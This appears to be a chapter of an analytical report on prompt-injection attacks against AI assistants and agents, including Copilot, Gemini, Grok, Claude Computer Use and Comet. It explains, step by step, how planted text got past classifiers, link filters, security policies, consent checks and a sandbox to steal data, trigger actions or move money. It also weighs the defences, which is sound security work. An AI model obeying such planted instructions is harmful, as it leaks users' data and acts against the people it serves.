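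Microsoft expected a classifier trained to recognise planted instructions to stop the email before it reached Copilot's language model. The researchers got past it by addressing the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioning Copilot or AI. Genuine business emails often contain instructions to their recipients, so a classifier strict enough to catch this one would probably block ordinary mail too. Ravia adds that developers have few good collections of real injections for training such classifiers.

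Next, Copilot has to retrieve the email while answering a question about something else. Microsoft has not published how Copilot's retrieval works, so Aim Labs reasoned from a common design. A program converts each passage of text into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and does the same with the question. It then retrieves the passages closest to the question, often measured by cosine similarity:

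similarity = (q · e) / (|q| |e|)

Here q is the embedding of the question and e is the embedding of a passage. The result is 1 when the two embeddings point in the same direction, and it falls as they diverge. A short email about one subject would be close to only a few questions. A long email is split into passages, each with its own embedding, so the researchers repeated their instructions under many headings, including employee onboarding, common HR questions and leave of absence. The question about leave then retrieves the passage on leave, which includes the instructions.

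Aim Labs had considered a subtler method of changing random characters in each copy of the instructions. A language model can still read the altered text, but the text's embedding changes. With one OpenAI embedding model, the similarity between a text and its altered copy fell as low as 0.7, lower than the similarity between the phrases "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science". The researchers could not tune this method to Copilot without knowing its embedding model, and the headings worked well enough. Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics, though Ravia does not say how often.

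The instructions ask the recipient to add the most sensitive item available to a web address. In the example, Copilot picks out the name Blue Heron from the earlier conversation. No control prevented Copilot from applying an outsider's instruction to internal data. Aim Labs calls this an "LLM scope violation" and considers it the core of the attack.

Copilot had a filter that removed external links from its answers. The filter recognised the usual Markdown links but missed reference-style links, which give the address on a separate line. With this bypass, the attack would work if the employee clicked the link.

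To remove the need for a click, the researchers had Copilot output an image in the same reference style. The filter missed this too, and the browser automatically tried to load the image, but Copilot's content security policy blocked the attacker's server.

However, the policy permitted many Microsoft hosts, so Aim Labs looked for one that would fetch an outside address on request. A SharePoint service did, but only if the employee had first accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. A Teams service did so without that condition. The browser requested the image from Teams, which the policy allowed. A Teams server then requested the address it had been given, which included "Blue Heron", from the attacker's server.

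Copilot's source citations were the last safeguard, since they might have led the employee to the strange email. The email contained an instruction never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that the employee would have seen nothing more suspicious than a broken link or image.

The attack could leak anything in the context window, including the chat history and any files Copilot had fetched to answer the employee's question. This is much less than the employee's whole mailbox. The attacker also did not choose the question, so one email might have leaked a trade secret or only the company's leave policy.

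### Evidence of use, and the repair

Ravia reports that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, a month before the details became public. The stolen data would have passed through a Teams server, so Microsoft may well have had records to check, but neither account of the attack describes what Microsoft examined. Any victims would have had little to notice, so they could not have provided much evidence.

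Reddy and Gujral, researchers at George Washington University, call EchoLeak the first real-world zero-click prompt injection exploit in a production system. "Real-world" here refers to the product, since the only known attackers were the researchers at Aim Labs. Willison describes EchoLeak as an extended version of leaks already seen in a dozen products. That is true of its use of an image and a web address, which Johann Rehberger had reported to Microsoft in 2023. Aim Labs' main advance was that the victim did not have to point Copilot at the attacker's text.

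According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft now strips reference-style links and embedded images from external content before Copilot reads it. They also propose marking all text from outside the organisation and telling the model not to follow instructions inside the marks. This may help, but the model can still follow instructions inside them. More strictly, they propose never putting external emails in the same context as internal documents. That would have stopped EchoLeak, but it would also prevent Copilot from doing the sort of task companies buy it for, such as comparing a customer's complaint with the contract.

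### Later attacks

Researchers have since found other chains in Microsoft's and Google's assistants. They differ in how much the victim has to do:

| Attack | Product | What the victim does | Type |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak (2025) | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asks a question that retrieves the planted email | Zero-click |
| GeminiJack (2025) | Gemini Enterprise | Runs a routine search | Zero-click |
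| SearchLeak (2026) | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Opens a link | One-click |
| CoSnitch, data theft (2026) | Copilot Personal | Opens a link | One-click |
| CoSnitch, false memories (2026) | Copilot Personal | Asks for a summary of the attacker's page | Request about a page |
| ChatMate (2026) | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Uploads a document and asks for help with it | Upload |
| Self-spreading instructions (2026) | Copilot in Word | Gives Copilot a document as source material | Upload or attachment |

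GeminiJack showed that the retrieval problem affected Google as well as Microsoft. Noma Security, which also found ForcedLeak, discovered the flaw in June 2025 and told Google the same day, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data*. It affected Gemini Enterprise, Google's set of AI tools for companies, and Vertex AI Search, which companies use to build their own search tools. The attacker put instructions in a Google document, a calendar invitation or an email.

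SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data* says the attack needed no user interaction, while SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* says an employee's routine search triggered it. Both descriptions fit a zero-click attack. The attack put emails, calendars and documents at risk. A shared document could reach more people than an email to one person, because it might turn up in searches by any employee with access to it.

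### SearchLeak

SearchLeak let the attacker write the question instead of waiting for a suitable one, as EchoLeak required. Copilot's enterprise search page accepted a query in its web address, much like the ChatGPT links Tenable reported in 2025. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) explains that Copilot treated this text as instructions and carried them out as soon as the employee opened the link. The link led to a genuine Microsoft site, so tools that block suspicious domains were unlikely to stop it.

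In the demonstration, the link made Copilot find an email and put its subject line in the address of an image. Microsoft also had a control for this, which wrapped Copilot's answers in a code block so that the browser would display any HTML as text without acting on it. But Copilot's answers appear on the screen as the model writes them, and the wrapping happened only when the answer was complete, so the browser loaded the image before then. This is a race condition, a flaw in which the outcome depends on which of two events happens first.

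The content security policy would still have blocked a direct request to the attacker's server, but it permitted requests to Bing, whose search-by-image feature fetched pictures from any address it received. Bing's server therefore sent the subject line to the attacker. EchoLeak had used Teams in the same way, and Bing was already on the list of permitted hosts that Aim Labs published in 2025. Microsoft closed the route through Teams but apparently either did not check the other hosts on the list for the same behaviour or did not find it.

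A subject line can be valuable because many services put one-time login codes there. Varonis says an attacker could also steal information such as salary data and acquisition plans, since Copilot can search everything the employee can open, but the published demonstration shows only the theft of a subject line. Varonis does not say whether anyone used the flaw.

Microsoft's official record of 4 June, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), classifies SearchLeak as command injection, a failure to neutralise special elements in a command. INCIBE's record classifies EchoLeak the same way. The definition fits the HTML tag in SearchLeak, which software can find and remove, better than the planted sentences in EchoLeak, which contained no special element to neutralise.

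Varonis recommends sanitizing each part of an answer before the browser displays it, and reviewing every allowlisted host that fetches URLs on request. Neither measure would stop a link from submitting instructions under the employee's identity. To prevent that, the search page would have to wait for the employee to confirm the query before running it.

### CoSnitch and memory

Varonis also found a related flaw in Copilot Personal, Microsoft's consumer assistant. A link to Copilot Personal could fill in a request, but the user normally had to press Enter to send it. *CoSnitch* (Varonis, 2026) describes an undocumented setting that, when added to the link, sent the request automatically. The researchers discovered it by asking Copilot why a link could not send a request by itself and questioning each explanation. Copilot's answers eventually included the setting's name and a claim that Microsoft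 had disabled it, but the setting still worked.

The request ran with access to whatever the user had connected, such as Gmail, Google Drive or a calendar, and continued even if the user closed the tab immediately. In one test, it made Copilot find the sender of the latest email, add their address to a URL and summarise that URL. Copilot opened the URL with its own page-reading tool, so this did not depend on the user's browser loading an image. In other tests, Copilot retrieved the full text of an email containing a password.

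CoSnitch also includes an ordinary indirect injection. When a user asks Copilot to summarise a web page, hidden text on the page makes Copilot save a false note in its memory. The summary looks normal. As with ChatGPT's memories, the note stays until the user deletes it, even if they change their password. Varonis used this method to make Copilot describe a known software vulnerability as harmless, which could mislead someone responsible for installing updates.

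Varonis presents CoSnitch as a danger to companies, but ThreatCluster's *CoSnitch Attack Exposes Microsoft Copilot Vulnerabilities* reports Microsoft's statement that enterprise customers were unaffected. Both can be true if company data is at risk only when an employee connects a work account to a personal assistant. ThreatCluster lists the flaw as CVE-2026-24301, with a severity score of 8.8. Microsoft released patches on 18 August 2026, and Varonis has seen no evidence of real attacks.

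Memory was also a weakness in the enterprise product. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* covers flaws in both versions of Copilot, including ones that let attackers plant memories and steal data through an HTML preview. Rehberger reported the flaws in 2025, and Microsoft has patched them.

### ChatMate and the way out of the sandbox

The chains so far send an attacker one batch of data, with no way to ask a follow-up question. In *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate*, Lahav (2026) of Rubrik Zero Labs, a security company's research group, describes a chain that allows a continuing exchange.

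The victim receives a Word document that reads like routine business correspondence but has instructions hidden behind a white rectangle. The victim uploads it to Microsoft 365 Copilot and asks for help filling in the details. For some tasks, Copilot writes a Python program and runs it in a sandbox without internet access. A safety layer is meant to refuse code that appears to probe the sandbox. Lahav got such code past this layer by presenting it as a harmless performance test, although in rare cases Copilot inspected the contents and refused.

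The code started with few permissions, but it could edit the script that had launched the sandbox, and that script ran with full administrator rights. Lahav added commands to the script and found a way to make it run them.

Even with administrator access, an attacker can't steal much from an isolated sandbox. Lahav spent a long time studying an unexplained service that the sandbox could reach, which saved a configuration file under any name it received. He couldn't see where the files went, but the service returned an error when a file already existed at the path he gave it, so he used it to test for thousands of known filenames. Some of the matches were files that appear only on a virtual machine's main system, which meant the service was writing to the host, the computer running the sandbox.

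The service did not check the names it received, which let Lahav control where it wrote and most of what it wrote. He then made the host load his own program with administrator rights. Microsoft's separation between customers kept him out of other customers' sandboxes, but the host could connect to the internet.

Lahav first used the connection only to copy uploaded files, which limited the attack because most of a company's mail and documents never enter the sandbox. He then realised that data could also travel inwards. The document instructed Copilot to treat the program's output as instructions and to send the results back to the program. An attacker's request goes over the internet to the host, from the host into the sandbox, and from there to Copilot as the output of its own code. Copilot carries out the request with the victim's permissions, and the answer returns by the same route.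 The attacker can read each answer and choose the next request until the conversation reaches its maximum number of turns. Lahav calls this remote prompt execution.

Microsoft had fixed the flaws before Lahav recorded the final demonstration, so he simulated the internet connection to the attacker. The rest of the demonstration is real. He suggests that a planted email or link could start the chain instead of an upload, but he did not demonstrate this. The flaw in the host service, CVE-2026-32193, has a severity score of 8.8 and also affected other products on Azure, Microsoft's cloud platform.

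The two-way channel did not depend on that service. PromptArmor built a similar loop in Copilot Cowork, Microsoft's agent for office tasks, and could use it to take emails and files from connected services. Pressing the stop button did not end the loop. PromptArmor reported the problem on 24 June 2026, and it had been mitigated by 19 August.

### Instructions that spread between Word documents

An attack can do lasting damage inside a company without sending data out. Måløy (2026), in *Context Collapse, Part 3*, describes hidden instructions that change the figures in a Word document and copy themselves into it. Content security policies and link filters do not stop this attack, because the attacker never needs to receive data.

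In one example, an employee downloads a market analysis containing hidden instructions from a trusted website that someone has compromised. The employee gives it to Copilot in Word as a source for a financial report. Copilot follows the instructions, alters the company's figures and copies the instructions into the new report. When a colleague uses that report as a source for another, the same thing happens without the original document.

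According to The Next Web's *A hidden line in a Word doc can rewrite your numbers*, the hidden text is white and in eight-point type, and Word removes colour and size before passing a document to the model. Gridinsoft's *Copilot Word AI Worm Can Spread Hidden Prompts Between Documents* notes that opening or sharing the file alone was not shown to start the attack; someone has to give the file to Copilot. The research project Morris II had already produced text that copied itself between AI email assistants, but Måløy believes his is among the first public demonstrations in a widely used office suite.

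Whether such a text spreads far depends on how people reuse documents. If each infected document becomes a source for n later ones, and Copilot copies the instructions with probability p, the average number of new carriers is:

R = n × p

With the invented values n = 3 and p = 0.5, R is 1.5, and one document leads to about eight new carriers in the fifth generation. If p falls to 0.3, R is 0.9 and the chain tends to die out. A defence can therefore stop an outbreak without blocking every copy, although each altered report still does harm. Måløy demonstrates the copying but gives no rate, so his work does not show how far the instructions would spread in a real company.

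Microsoft tried two mitigations. On 3 April 2026 it released a new way of editing with Copilot in Word, which stopped Måløy's original wording. He confirmed this on 9 April and, the same day, got the attack working again with a different task, manipulating financial figures. In July, Microsoft moved the product to a newer model, GPT-5.5. The next day, Måløy reproduced the attack on the even newer GPT-5.6. The attack still worked when he published on 28 July, so he withheld the exact text. Gridinsoft found no public evidence that the attack had been used against real organisations.

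Måløy advises people to treat outside documents as untrusted and to check Copilot's drafts before sharing them. Checking the figures against their original source would catch the alterations, though it uses up some of the time Copilot saved. A rule about outside documents protects only the first employee. The colleague would have no reason to distrust a report written by someone they know inside the company, and a filter that checks the author would not flag it. To flag such a report, Word would have to record that an outside document had contributed to it and keep that record through every later draft.

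## Emails, invitations and posts that make an assistant act

The hidden text in Måløy's Word documents changed only what Copilot wrote. If an assistant has access to other systems, planted text can also make it delete a calendar appointment, switch on a boiler or send money from a wallet.

The attacker sends an email, an invitation or a message that tells the assistant to take an action. Nothing happens until the user asks an ordinary question, such as what is on the calendar this week. The assistant then reads the week's events, including the attacker's invitation. If the model follows the planted instruction, it writes a tool call, a short piece of structured text that the product's software carries out.

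Suppose the assistant has tools to read the calendar, delete events and control the heating. The user's question needs only the first, but the developer's instructions describe all three to the model. If the model calls the heating tool, the call doesn't show whether the user or an event title prompted it.

### Waiting for the user's next reply

Google anticipated part of this problem. In November 2023, Johann Rehberger tested Bard, the Google chatbot now called Gemini. Planted instructions could make it search for flights or hotels, but it would not open the user's mail or documents in the same turn (one user message and the assistant's reply).

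Embrace The Red's *Google Gemini* describes how Rehberger got around this with a delayed tool call. He wrote an email telling Gemini to wait for the user's next request, then find a document about cats in the user's Google Drive and print it. When the user had Gemini read the email and then asked for something else, Gemini fetched the document.

The check failed because it covered only the turn in which Gemini read the email. No new outside text came in during the next turn, so Gemini could use the tool again. But the planted instruction was still in the context window as part of the earlier conversation.

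The harm was limited at first because Google had already closed the image channel that could have carried the document to an attacker. Techzine reports that Google took no further steps against delayed tool calls because it knew of no other way for the data to get out. In December 2024, Rehberger reported an attack that didn't need to send data anywhere. He had Gemini summarise a document about Albert Einstein, and text planted in the document made the summary end with an offer to say more. When the user answered, Gemini saved false facts about the user to its long-term memory. According to Embrace The Red's *Hacking Gemini's Memory with Prompt Injection and Delayed Tool Invocation*, Google rated both the likelihood and the impact as low.

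Rehberger proposes requiring the user's confirmation for every sensitive action once untrusted text has entered the conversation. This prevents injected text from triggering such an action in a later turn without the user's approval, but a user who asks for a summary of their email would then have to approve every sensitive action for the rest of that conversation.

### "Invitation Is All You Need"

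Delayed calls became much more serious when Gemini gained tools that could change things. In *Invitation Is All You Need*, Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025) attacked Gemini's web app, its mobile app, and the version of Google Assistant that runs on Gemini. They put instructions in the titles of calendar invitations, the subject lines of emails and the names of shared files.

The attacker needs the victim's email address and must get an invitation onto the victim's calendar. Google lets users add invitations from everyone, only from known senders, or only after responding to them. The researchers assume that most people never change the default. The stricter settings do little against an attacker the victim knows, such as a spouse, a boss or a former friend.

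Gemini's main model plans each task and hands parts of it to specialised agents, such as those for mail, the calendar and home devices. Google had separated these agents so that only the main model could start one, and each returned only its output, not its working text. But the calendar agent's output includes event titles, so a title planted by an attacker reached the main model, which could start any of the other agents.

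The researchers sort their 14 scenarios into five classes:

| Class | What the planted text does | Outcomes |
|---|---|---|
| Short-term context poisoning | Changes Gemini's replies in the current conversation | Abuse read aloud, spam, phishing |
| Long-term memory poisoning | Saves a false note for later conversations | Disinformation |
| Tool misuse | Makes the agent that read the text use another of its own tools | Calendar events deleted or added |
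| Automatic agent invocation | Starts a different agent | Windows opened, boiler switched on, lights controlled |
| Automatic app invocation | Opens another app on an Android phone | Video streamed, user located, file downloaded, meetings or emails leaked, worm |

In the home tests, a user asked Gemini about upcoming events and then thanked it. The thanks triggered the delayed call, and Gemini opened the apartment's windows, switched on the boiler or turned on the lights. In another test, the thanks made Gemini open Zoom and join the attacker's meeting, which streamed video of the user. Gemini could also open a web page in the phone's browser, and the page's server could then estimate the phone's location from its IP address. In one test, the web address contained the titles of six of the user's meetings.

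The researchers ran these attacks on their own accounts and in their own surroundings. They filmed the attacks but give no success rates, and they didn't demonstrate all 14 scenarios separately. They infer from the spam test that phishing would work, rely on Rehberger's earlier work for disinformation, and describe the worm as something an attacker could build from the email leak.

*The Promptware Kill Chain* (2026), which breaks such attacks into stages, finds no reconnaissance stage in the Zoom attack. Without a first step to check what the planted text can reach, the attacker has to guess. For example, an invitation with instructions for Gemini to open the windows does nothing in a home without connected windows.

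### How the researchers rated the risks

Nassi and colleagues adapted a method that carmakers use for cybersecurity. They scored each attack from 0 to 3 on six factors and took the average as its likelihood. For most of the attacks, an ordinary laptop was enough (3), the attacker needed the skills of a computing graduate (2), could strike at any time (3), had to know only an email address (2), could prepare in less than a day (3) and relied on a question that users ask often (2):

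(3 + 2 + 3 + 2 + 3 + 2) / 6 = 2.5

A score of 2.4 or higher counts as "very likely". This likelihood is then combined with the worst of four kinds of harm: financial, operational, safety and privacy.

The researchers rated four risks as critical: streaming video of the user, opening the windows, stealing emails, and the worm. They rated phishing and the theft of meeting details as very high, and control of the boiler and lights, location tracking and abusive speech as high. They rated opening the windows as critical for privacy, because someone could photograph the resident through them, and one step lower for burglary. They report that 73% of the risks were high or above, but their list has 10 of 14, which is 71%.

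The likelihood score is higher the less an attacker needs to carry out the attack. It doesn't account for how often the attack works on Gemini, so an attack that worked once in ten attempts would score the same as one that always worked.

The researchers also estimated the risk that would remain if Google adopted a set of five defences. They assumed that an attacker would then need a cluster of expensive processors, expert skills and months of work. On those assumptions, the average likelihood score falls to 7/6 (about 1.17), just under the limit of 1.2 for "unlikely", and the critical risks become medium. These estimates are judgements about a future attacker, and the paper reports no test of the defences.

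One of the five would run the user's request twice, with and without the outside text, and ask the user to confirm if the resulting actions differed. A question about next week's events should not make the assistant open a window in either run. This would catch many attacks, but it roughly doubles the work, and some honest requests depend on the outside text. For example, a user who asks Gemini to accept any invitation from the dentist wants those invitations to change what it does.

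### Google's changes and SafeBreach's second attack

The researchers reported their findings on 22 February 2025, and Google asked for 90 days. It then began requiring confirmation for risky actions that involve a user's documents, several apps or home devices. It also handled suspicious web addresses more strictly and improved the classifiers that detect planted instructions. Google says it reran the original attacks with many variations and confirmed that the defences worked. The same statement called the techniques theoretical, although the researchers had filmed them working on Google's products.

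*Gemini's Secret Affair* (2026) describes how Yair's employer, the security company SafeBreach, then moved from invitations to instant messages. Gemini can read out a phone's notifications, so anyone who can trigger a notification, through WhatsApp, Slack or a text message, can get text into the model's input.

With Google's new defence against delayed calls, Gemini at first refused all of SafeBreach's attempts to plant an action that would wait for a word such as "thanks". It would still open a window if it had first asked the user and the user had said yes. SafeBreach concluded that the check probably compared Gemini's last message with the user's reply to decide whether the user had consented. SafeBreach then got past the check by making the user's "yes" to a harmless question count as the answer to another question that the user had not noticed.

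This made Gemini open the windows and start the Zoom stream again. It also made Gemini save a false name for the user in its long-term memory and schedule a daily task to read out the user's recent messages, which the earlier attacks had not done. In a separate attack that needed no tools, Gemini reported an invented message from one of the user's real contacts. The attacker didn't have to know the contact's name, because Gemini took it from the other notifications. Someone who is driving and cannot look at the screen would have little reason to doubt the message.

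SafeBreach reported these findings on 17 August 2025. On 14 November, Google confirmed that an improved classifier now stopped the attacks. The fix therefore depends on a model recognising planted text, and SafeBreach does not say whether Google also changed the consent check.

### Private meetings copied into a new event

In January 2026, the security company Miggo published another attack that used calendar invitations, this time to steal information without any web request. SiliconANGLE's *Indirect prompt injection in Google Gemini enabled unauthorized access to meeting data* (2026) describes the attack in three stages. The attacker first sends an invitation with an instruction in its description. Gemini does not act on the instruction until the user asks about their schedule. TechRepublic's *Google Gemini Flaw Let Attackers Access Private Calendar Data* gives the example of asking whether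 they are free on a certain day. Gemini then summarises the user's private meetings and writes the summary into the description of a new event.

Under some companies' settings, the attacker could read the summary in the new event. A content security policy or a check on outgoing links would not have helped, because the data never left Google Calendar, which both Gemini and the attacker could use.

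The instruction was in ordinary language, and each step was something a user might really ask for, such as summarising meetings or creating an event. Miggo argues that this let it get past Google's detection, because the text became harmful only when Gemini carried it out with the user's access. Google confirmed the finding and has fixed the flaw. SiliconANGLE does not give a success rate or mention Gemini asking for the user's approval before it created the event, although Google had expanded its use of confirmation requests the year before.

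### Messages that copy themselves

If a planted email can make an assistant send mail, it might also make the assistant send copies of that email. Stav Cohen, Ron Bitton and Ben Nassi tested this in 2024 with a text-based computer worm they called Morris II. A computer worm is malicious software that spreads by copying itself.

*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reviews an experiment in which the planted text had three parts: one to make the model obey, one to make it repeat the whole text in its output, and one to do the harm. An email assistant stored the message containing this text with the user's other mail. Later, while drafting an email, it retrieved the message as background, copied the text into the draft and added sensitive details from the user's mail. The recipient's assistant then stored that email, and the process could repeat.

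The researchers tested Morris II in a system with 2,000 messages from 20 employees of Enron, the bankrupt energy company whose emails are public. In one configuration, about one in five of the generated messages compromised a new assistant. At that rate, a compromised assistant would have to write to more than five new assistants on average for the worm to grow. An assistant that answers mail all day could reach that number, but only if it stored, retrieved and sent messages without anyone checking them. No one has reported the worm spreading through public email.

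A later replication suggests that the weakness was not limited to the first models. *Responsible Development of Offensive AI* (2025) repeated the attack with Falcon3, an open model released in December 2024, and found that it still worked, again in a test system.

Researchers have since shown parts of such a worm on real products. ZombieAgent needed the attacker's server to send the new emails, and Måløy's text spread only when a person gave each infected document to Copilot. Studies of agents that message each other, such as *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026), have been limited to controlled environments.

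### A theft of cryptocurrency

The Gemini attacks were demonstrations, but in May 2026 someone used a similar weakness to take real money. Bankrbot is a bot on the social network X that creates and transfers cryptocurrency tokens when people post commands to it. Its operator, Bankr, had automatically set up a wallet for the X account of Grok, xAI's chatbot. According to BeInCrypto's *How AI Was Tricked Into Stealing $150,000 From Grok Wallet*, Bankr's founder said nobody at xAI administered the wallet and Grok's posts alone controlled it.

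The attacker first sent Grok's wallet an NFT, a unique digital token, which enabled the wallet to make transfers. The attacker then posted a message to Grok in Morse code. CryptoSlate's *Grok’s crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet* reconstructs the rest from posts on X. Grok decoded the message and posted the result, a command to Bankrbot to send DRB tokens. Bankrbot treated the post as an order from the wallet's owner and transferred 3 billion of them.

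BeInCrypto puts the sum at about $150,000, while OECD's *AI Prompt Injection Exploit Drains Grok-Linked Crypto Wallet* (2026), an AI-generated entry in an incident register, gives a range of $150,000 to $200,000. Bankr says that 80% was returned and that the rest is in dispute, but an article on MEXC, a cryptocurrency exchange, says that all of it was returned.

The attacker wrote to Grok openly, as any X user can, so the attack on Grok was a direct injection. Bankrbot was the confused deputy, because it received a clear order from an account it trusted and did not process the Morse code itself. A filter on the attacker's post would have had to decode the message to detect the attack.

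Bankr had some warning from an incident in March 2025, when Grok's exchanges with Bankrbot led to the creation of 17 tokens, one of which reached a market value of $30 million. The developers then cut off Grok's access, according to OECD's *Grok AI Breaks Free, Creates Crypto Tokens, Bankrbot Disables Interactions* (2025). By May 2026, Bankrbot was evidently acting on Grok's instructions again.

An attacker can also achieve the same result through an assistant's stored memory. Suppose a finance assistant reads an email that gives a false account number for the user's landlord, and saves the number. Weeks later the user asks it to pay the rent, and it sends the money to the attacker. A confirmation that showed only the landlord's name and the amount would look correct.

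### Planted requests for payment

Attackers have also left payment instructions on web pages for any agent that reads them. The security company Forcepoint found one page with a PayPal link, a fixed amount of $5,000 and full steps for completing the payment. The researcher Sewani argues in Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* that such exact instructions point to an attack ready for use rather than a test. The detail does suggest that the writer wanted the money, but it is little evidence of whether any agent would pay, and no payment is known.

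In July 2026, another security company, Zscaler, described two campaigns that took more effort. The attackers pushed their pages up the search rankings so that agents would find them. *Hidden Web Prompts Trick AI Agents Into Sending Money* (Paganini, 2026) reports that one site targeted coding assistants by posing as the documentation for a Python library called requests-secure-v2. Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* adds that this site ran a payment scam, while the other impersonated a cryptocurrency service. The pages are evidence of intent, but confirming a theft would require tracing a payment from an agent to one of the attackers.

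### Which controls stopped an action

The published attacks provide a rough test of several controls:

| Control | What it stopped | What got past it |
|---|---|---|
| Separate agents for separate services | Direct calls from one agent to another | Planted text in the calendar agent's output |
| No sensitive tools in the turn that reads outside text | Immediate access to mail and documents | Calls delayed until the next turn |
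| Check that the user's reply amounts to consent | All of SafeBreach's plain delayed calls | Consent to a question the user had not noticed |
| Wider user confirmations at Google | The 2025 attacks, in Google's own tests alongside its other changes | No independent test of this control alone |
| Spending limits and lists of approved recipients | No published test | No published test |

Separating the agents failed because the main model still read what they returned and had access to every tool. A stricter design would take tools away from the main model once it had read outside text, so that a question about the calendar could not trigger the heating system. This would be less convenient for users, because a request such as "switch on the heating before my first meeting" needs both the calendar and the heating system.

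Confirmation is stronger when the product's own software handles it. SafeBreach succeeded because Google's check apparently inferred consent from a conversation that the attacker could partly write. A fixed dialog with the text "Open the living-room window?" and a button would be much harder for planted text to manipulate. The dialog would have to appear before the action took effect, unlike Notion's warning, and show the important details, such as the account number for a payment. Nassi and colleagues also suggest a short countdown with a cancel button, but only as a last resort because it relies on the user to notice the attack.

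Gavish (2026) writes in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that Google can change its rules on confirmation and tool combinations through simple settings, faster than it can retrain a model. He also says that indirect injection can't be solved once and then left alone.

Wallet software can enforce a payment limit that a post can't override. With a limit of $500 a day, emptying a $150,000 wallet would take 300 days, and someone would probably notice. A list of approved recipients would have blocked the transfer to the attacker's address. Some early wallet agents also needed a person to complete each transaction, according to the article on MEXC. But Bankr's wallet gained its transfer powers from a token that a stranger could send it, and a spending limit would not have protected it either if such a token could lift the limit.

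## Agents that operate a browser or a computer

Gemini could open a window or delete an appointment only because Google had given it tools for those actions. An agent that operates a browser clicks and types on the same pages as its user. It can therefore do much of what the user can do on any website where they are logged in, without needing a separate tool for each service.

### How the agent uses a page

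Suppose a user asks an agentic browser to book a flight to London next Friday. The browser sends the model this request with a screenshot of the current page, text from the page's DOM (document object model, the browser's internal record of everything on the page), or both. The model outputs an action, such as clicking the search box or typing text. The browser carries out the action and sends the model the updated page. This loop repeats until the task is finished.

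Booking a flight may take dozens of rounds, and each one adds material to the context window. Earlier pages can stay there because the model may need them to compare prices or check a date. Text planted on one page can therefore affect what the agent does on later pages.

An agent that relies on the DOM can also receive a different description of a button from the one a person sees. *The Verifiable Action Card* (2026) explains that such agents label buttons and other elements using attributes in the page's code, which an attacker can change without altering the page's appearance.

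Computer-use agents apply the same loop to a whole desktop. Anthropic released one, Claude Computer Use, as a public beta in October 2024. *Indirect Prompt Injection of Claude Computer Use* (Martin, 2024) describes how the agent viewed the screen through screenshots, controlled the mouse and keyboard, and ran shell commands, which are typed instructions to the operating system.

Within days, Johann Rehberger had used a web page to make Claude install malware. The page contained instructions for the computer to download a "support tool" and launch it. Claude clicked the link, found the downloaded file, changed its permissions so that it could run, and started it. The program then connected to a server that let an attacker control the machine. Willison (2024), in *ZombAIs*, called the attack "pretty much the simplest thing that can possibly work". However, Hackaday's *Prompt Injection Tricks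 AI Into Downloading And Executing Malware* (2025) reports that the attack worked once Rehberger called the malware a support tool and put the instructions in the body of the page.

Embrace The Red's *ZombAIs* presents this as a fundamental design problem in agents rather than a mistake specific to Claude. The attacker gained little of value because the agent ran on a virtual machine set up for the test, but an agentic browser often runs on the user's own computer, where the user may be logged in to email, work and bank accounts.

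### The same-origin policy

Browsers have long had to let people open an untrustworthy site in one tab and their bank in another. The same-origin policy, introduced in 1995, makes this reasonably safe by stopping one website from reading another site's data. A page's origin has three parts:

origin = (scheme, host, port)

For http://www.example.com/dir/page.html, the scheme is http, the host is www.example.com and the port (a number that identifies a service on the host) is 80 by default. These three parts make up the page's origin, and a script on one page can read data from another only if their origins match. The encrypted version of the same page has a different origin because it uses https and port 443.

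The same-origin policy restricts scripts but not the user, who may copy an account number from the bank's page and paste it into any other site. An agent can do the same by reading the number on the bank's page, keeping it in its context window and typing it into another site. The policy doesn't block this because the agent is only reading and typing as a user would, and no script has crossed from one origin to another.

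Malicious instructions on one page can also make an agent act on another site. Websites already had a similar problem, called cross-site request forgery, in which a malicious page made the browser send a request to another site, such as an order to transfer money. The browser attached the user's cookies, which keep the user logged in, so the request appeared to come from the user. Web developers responded by requiring a secret value that appears only in the site's own forms. This doesn't stop a hijacked agent, because the agent opens the real form and submits it with the secret included.

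Other familiar web attacks also work on agents, according to research by Datta and colleagues (*WAAA! Web Adversaries Against Agentic Browsers*) cited in *The Verifiable Action Card*. *The Agent Clicks Approve* (2026) studies two actions whose effects last after the agent has stopped: approving an outside application's request for access to the user's account, and registering a web address to which a service will send the account's future events. Each takes a single form submission, and closing the browser afterwards does not cancel it.

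### The Comet exploit

Brave found an attack on Perplexity's Comet browser in July 2025 that moved data between three websites. Chaikin and Sahib, in *Agentic Browser Security*, describe a demonstration in which the carrier was a Reddit comment, with the instructions behind a spoiler tag that hides text until a reader clicks on it. The victim opened the post and clicked Comet's button to summarise the page. Comet passed part of the page to its model without separating it from the user's request, and the agent did the following:

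1. It opened the user's account page on Perplexity's website and read their email address.
2. It entered the address on a Perplexity login page, which made Perplexity email the user a one-time code.
3. It opened Gmail, where the user was already logged in, and read the code.
4. It replied to the Reddit comment with the email address and the code.

The attacker could read the reply and use its contents to take over the victim's Perplexity account. The victim did nothing after clicking the button.

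The second step needed a workaround, because Perplexity would not normally send a code to a user who was already logged in. The planted text used a slightly different form of Perplexity's web address, which led to the same service but counted as a different domain. The existing login did not apply there, so the agent could start a new login.

A script in the Reddit comment could not have carried out this attack, because the same-origin policy would have prevented it from reading either Perplexity's account page or Gmail. The one-time code was meant to show that the person logging in controlled the mailbox, but it failed as a safeguard because the agent had access to that mailbox.

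Chaikin and Sahib give no success rate, but they describe the steps in enough detail that Perplexity could have checked them. Perplexity acknowledged the flaw two days after the report and released a fix, which Brave found incomplete the next day. A later fix seemed to work on 13 August, but after Brave published its findings on 20 August, it found that Perplexity had still not fully stopped this kind of attack.

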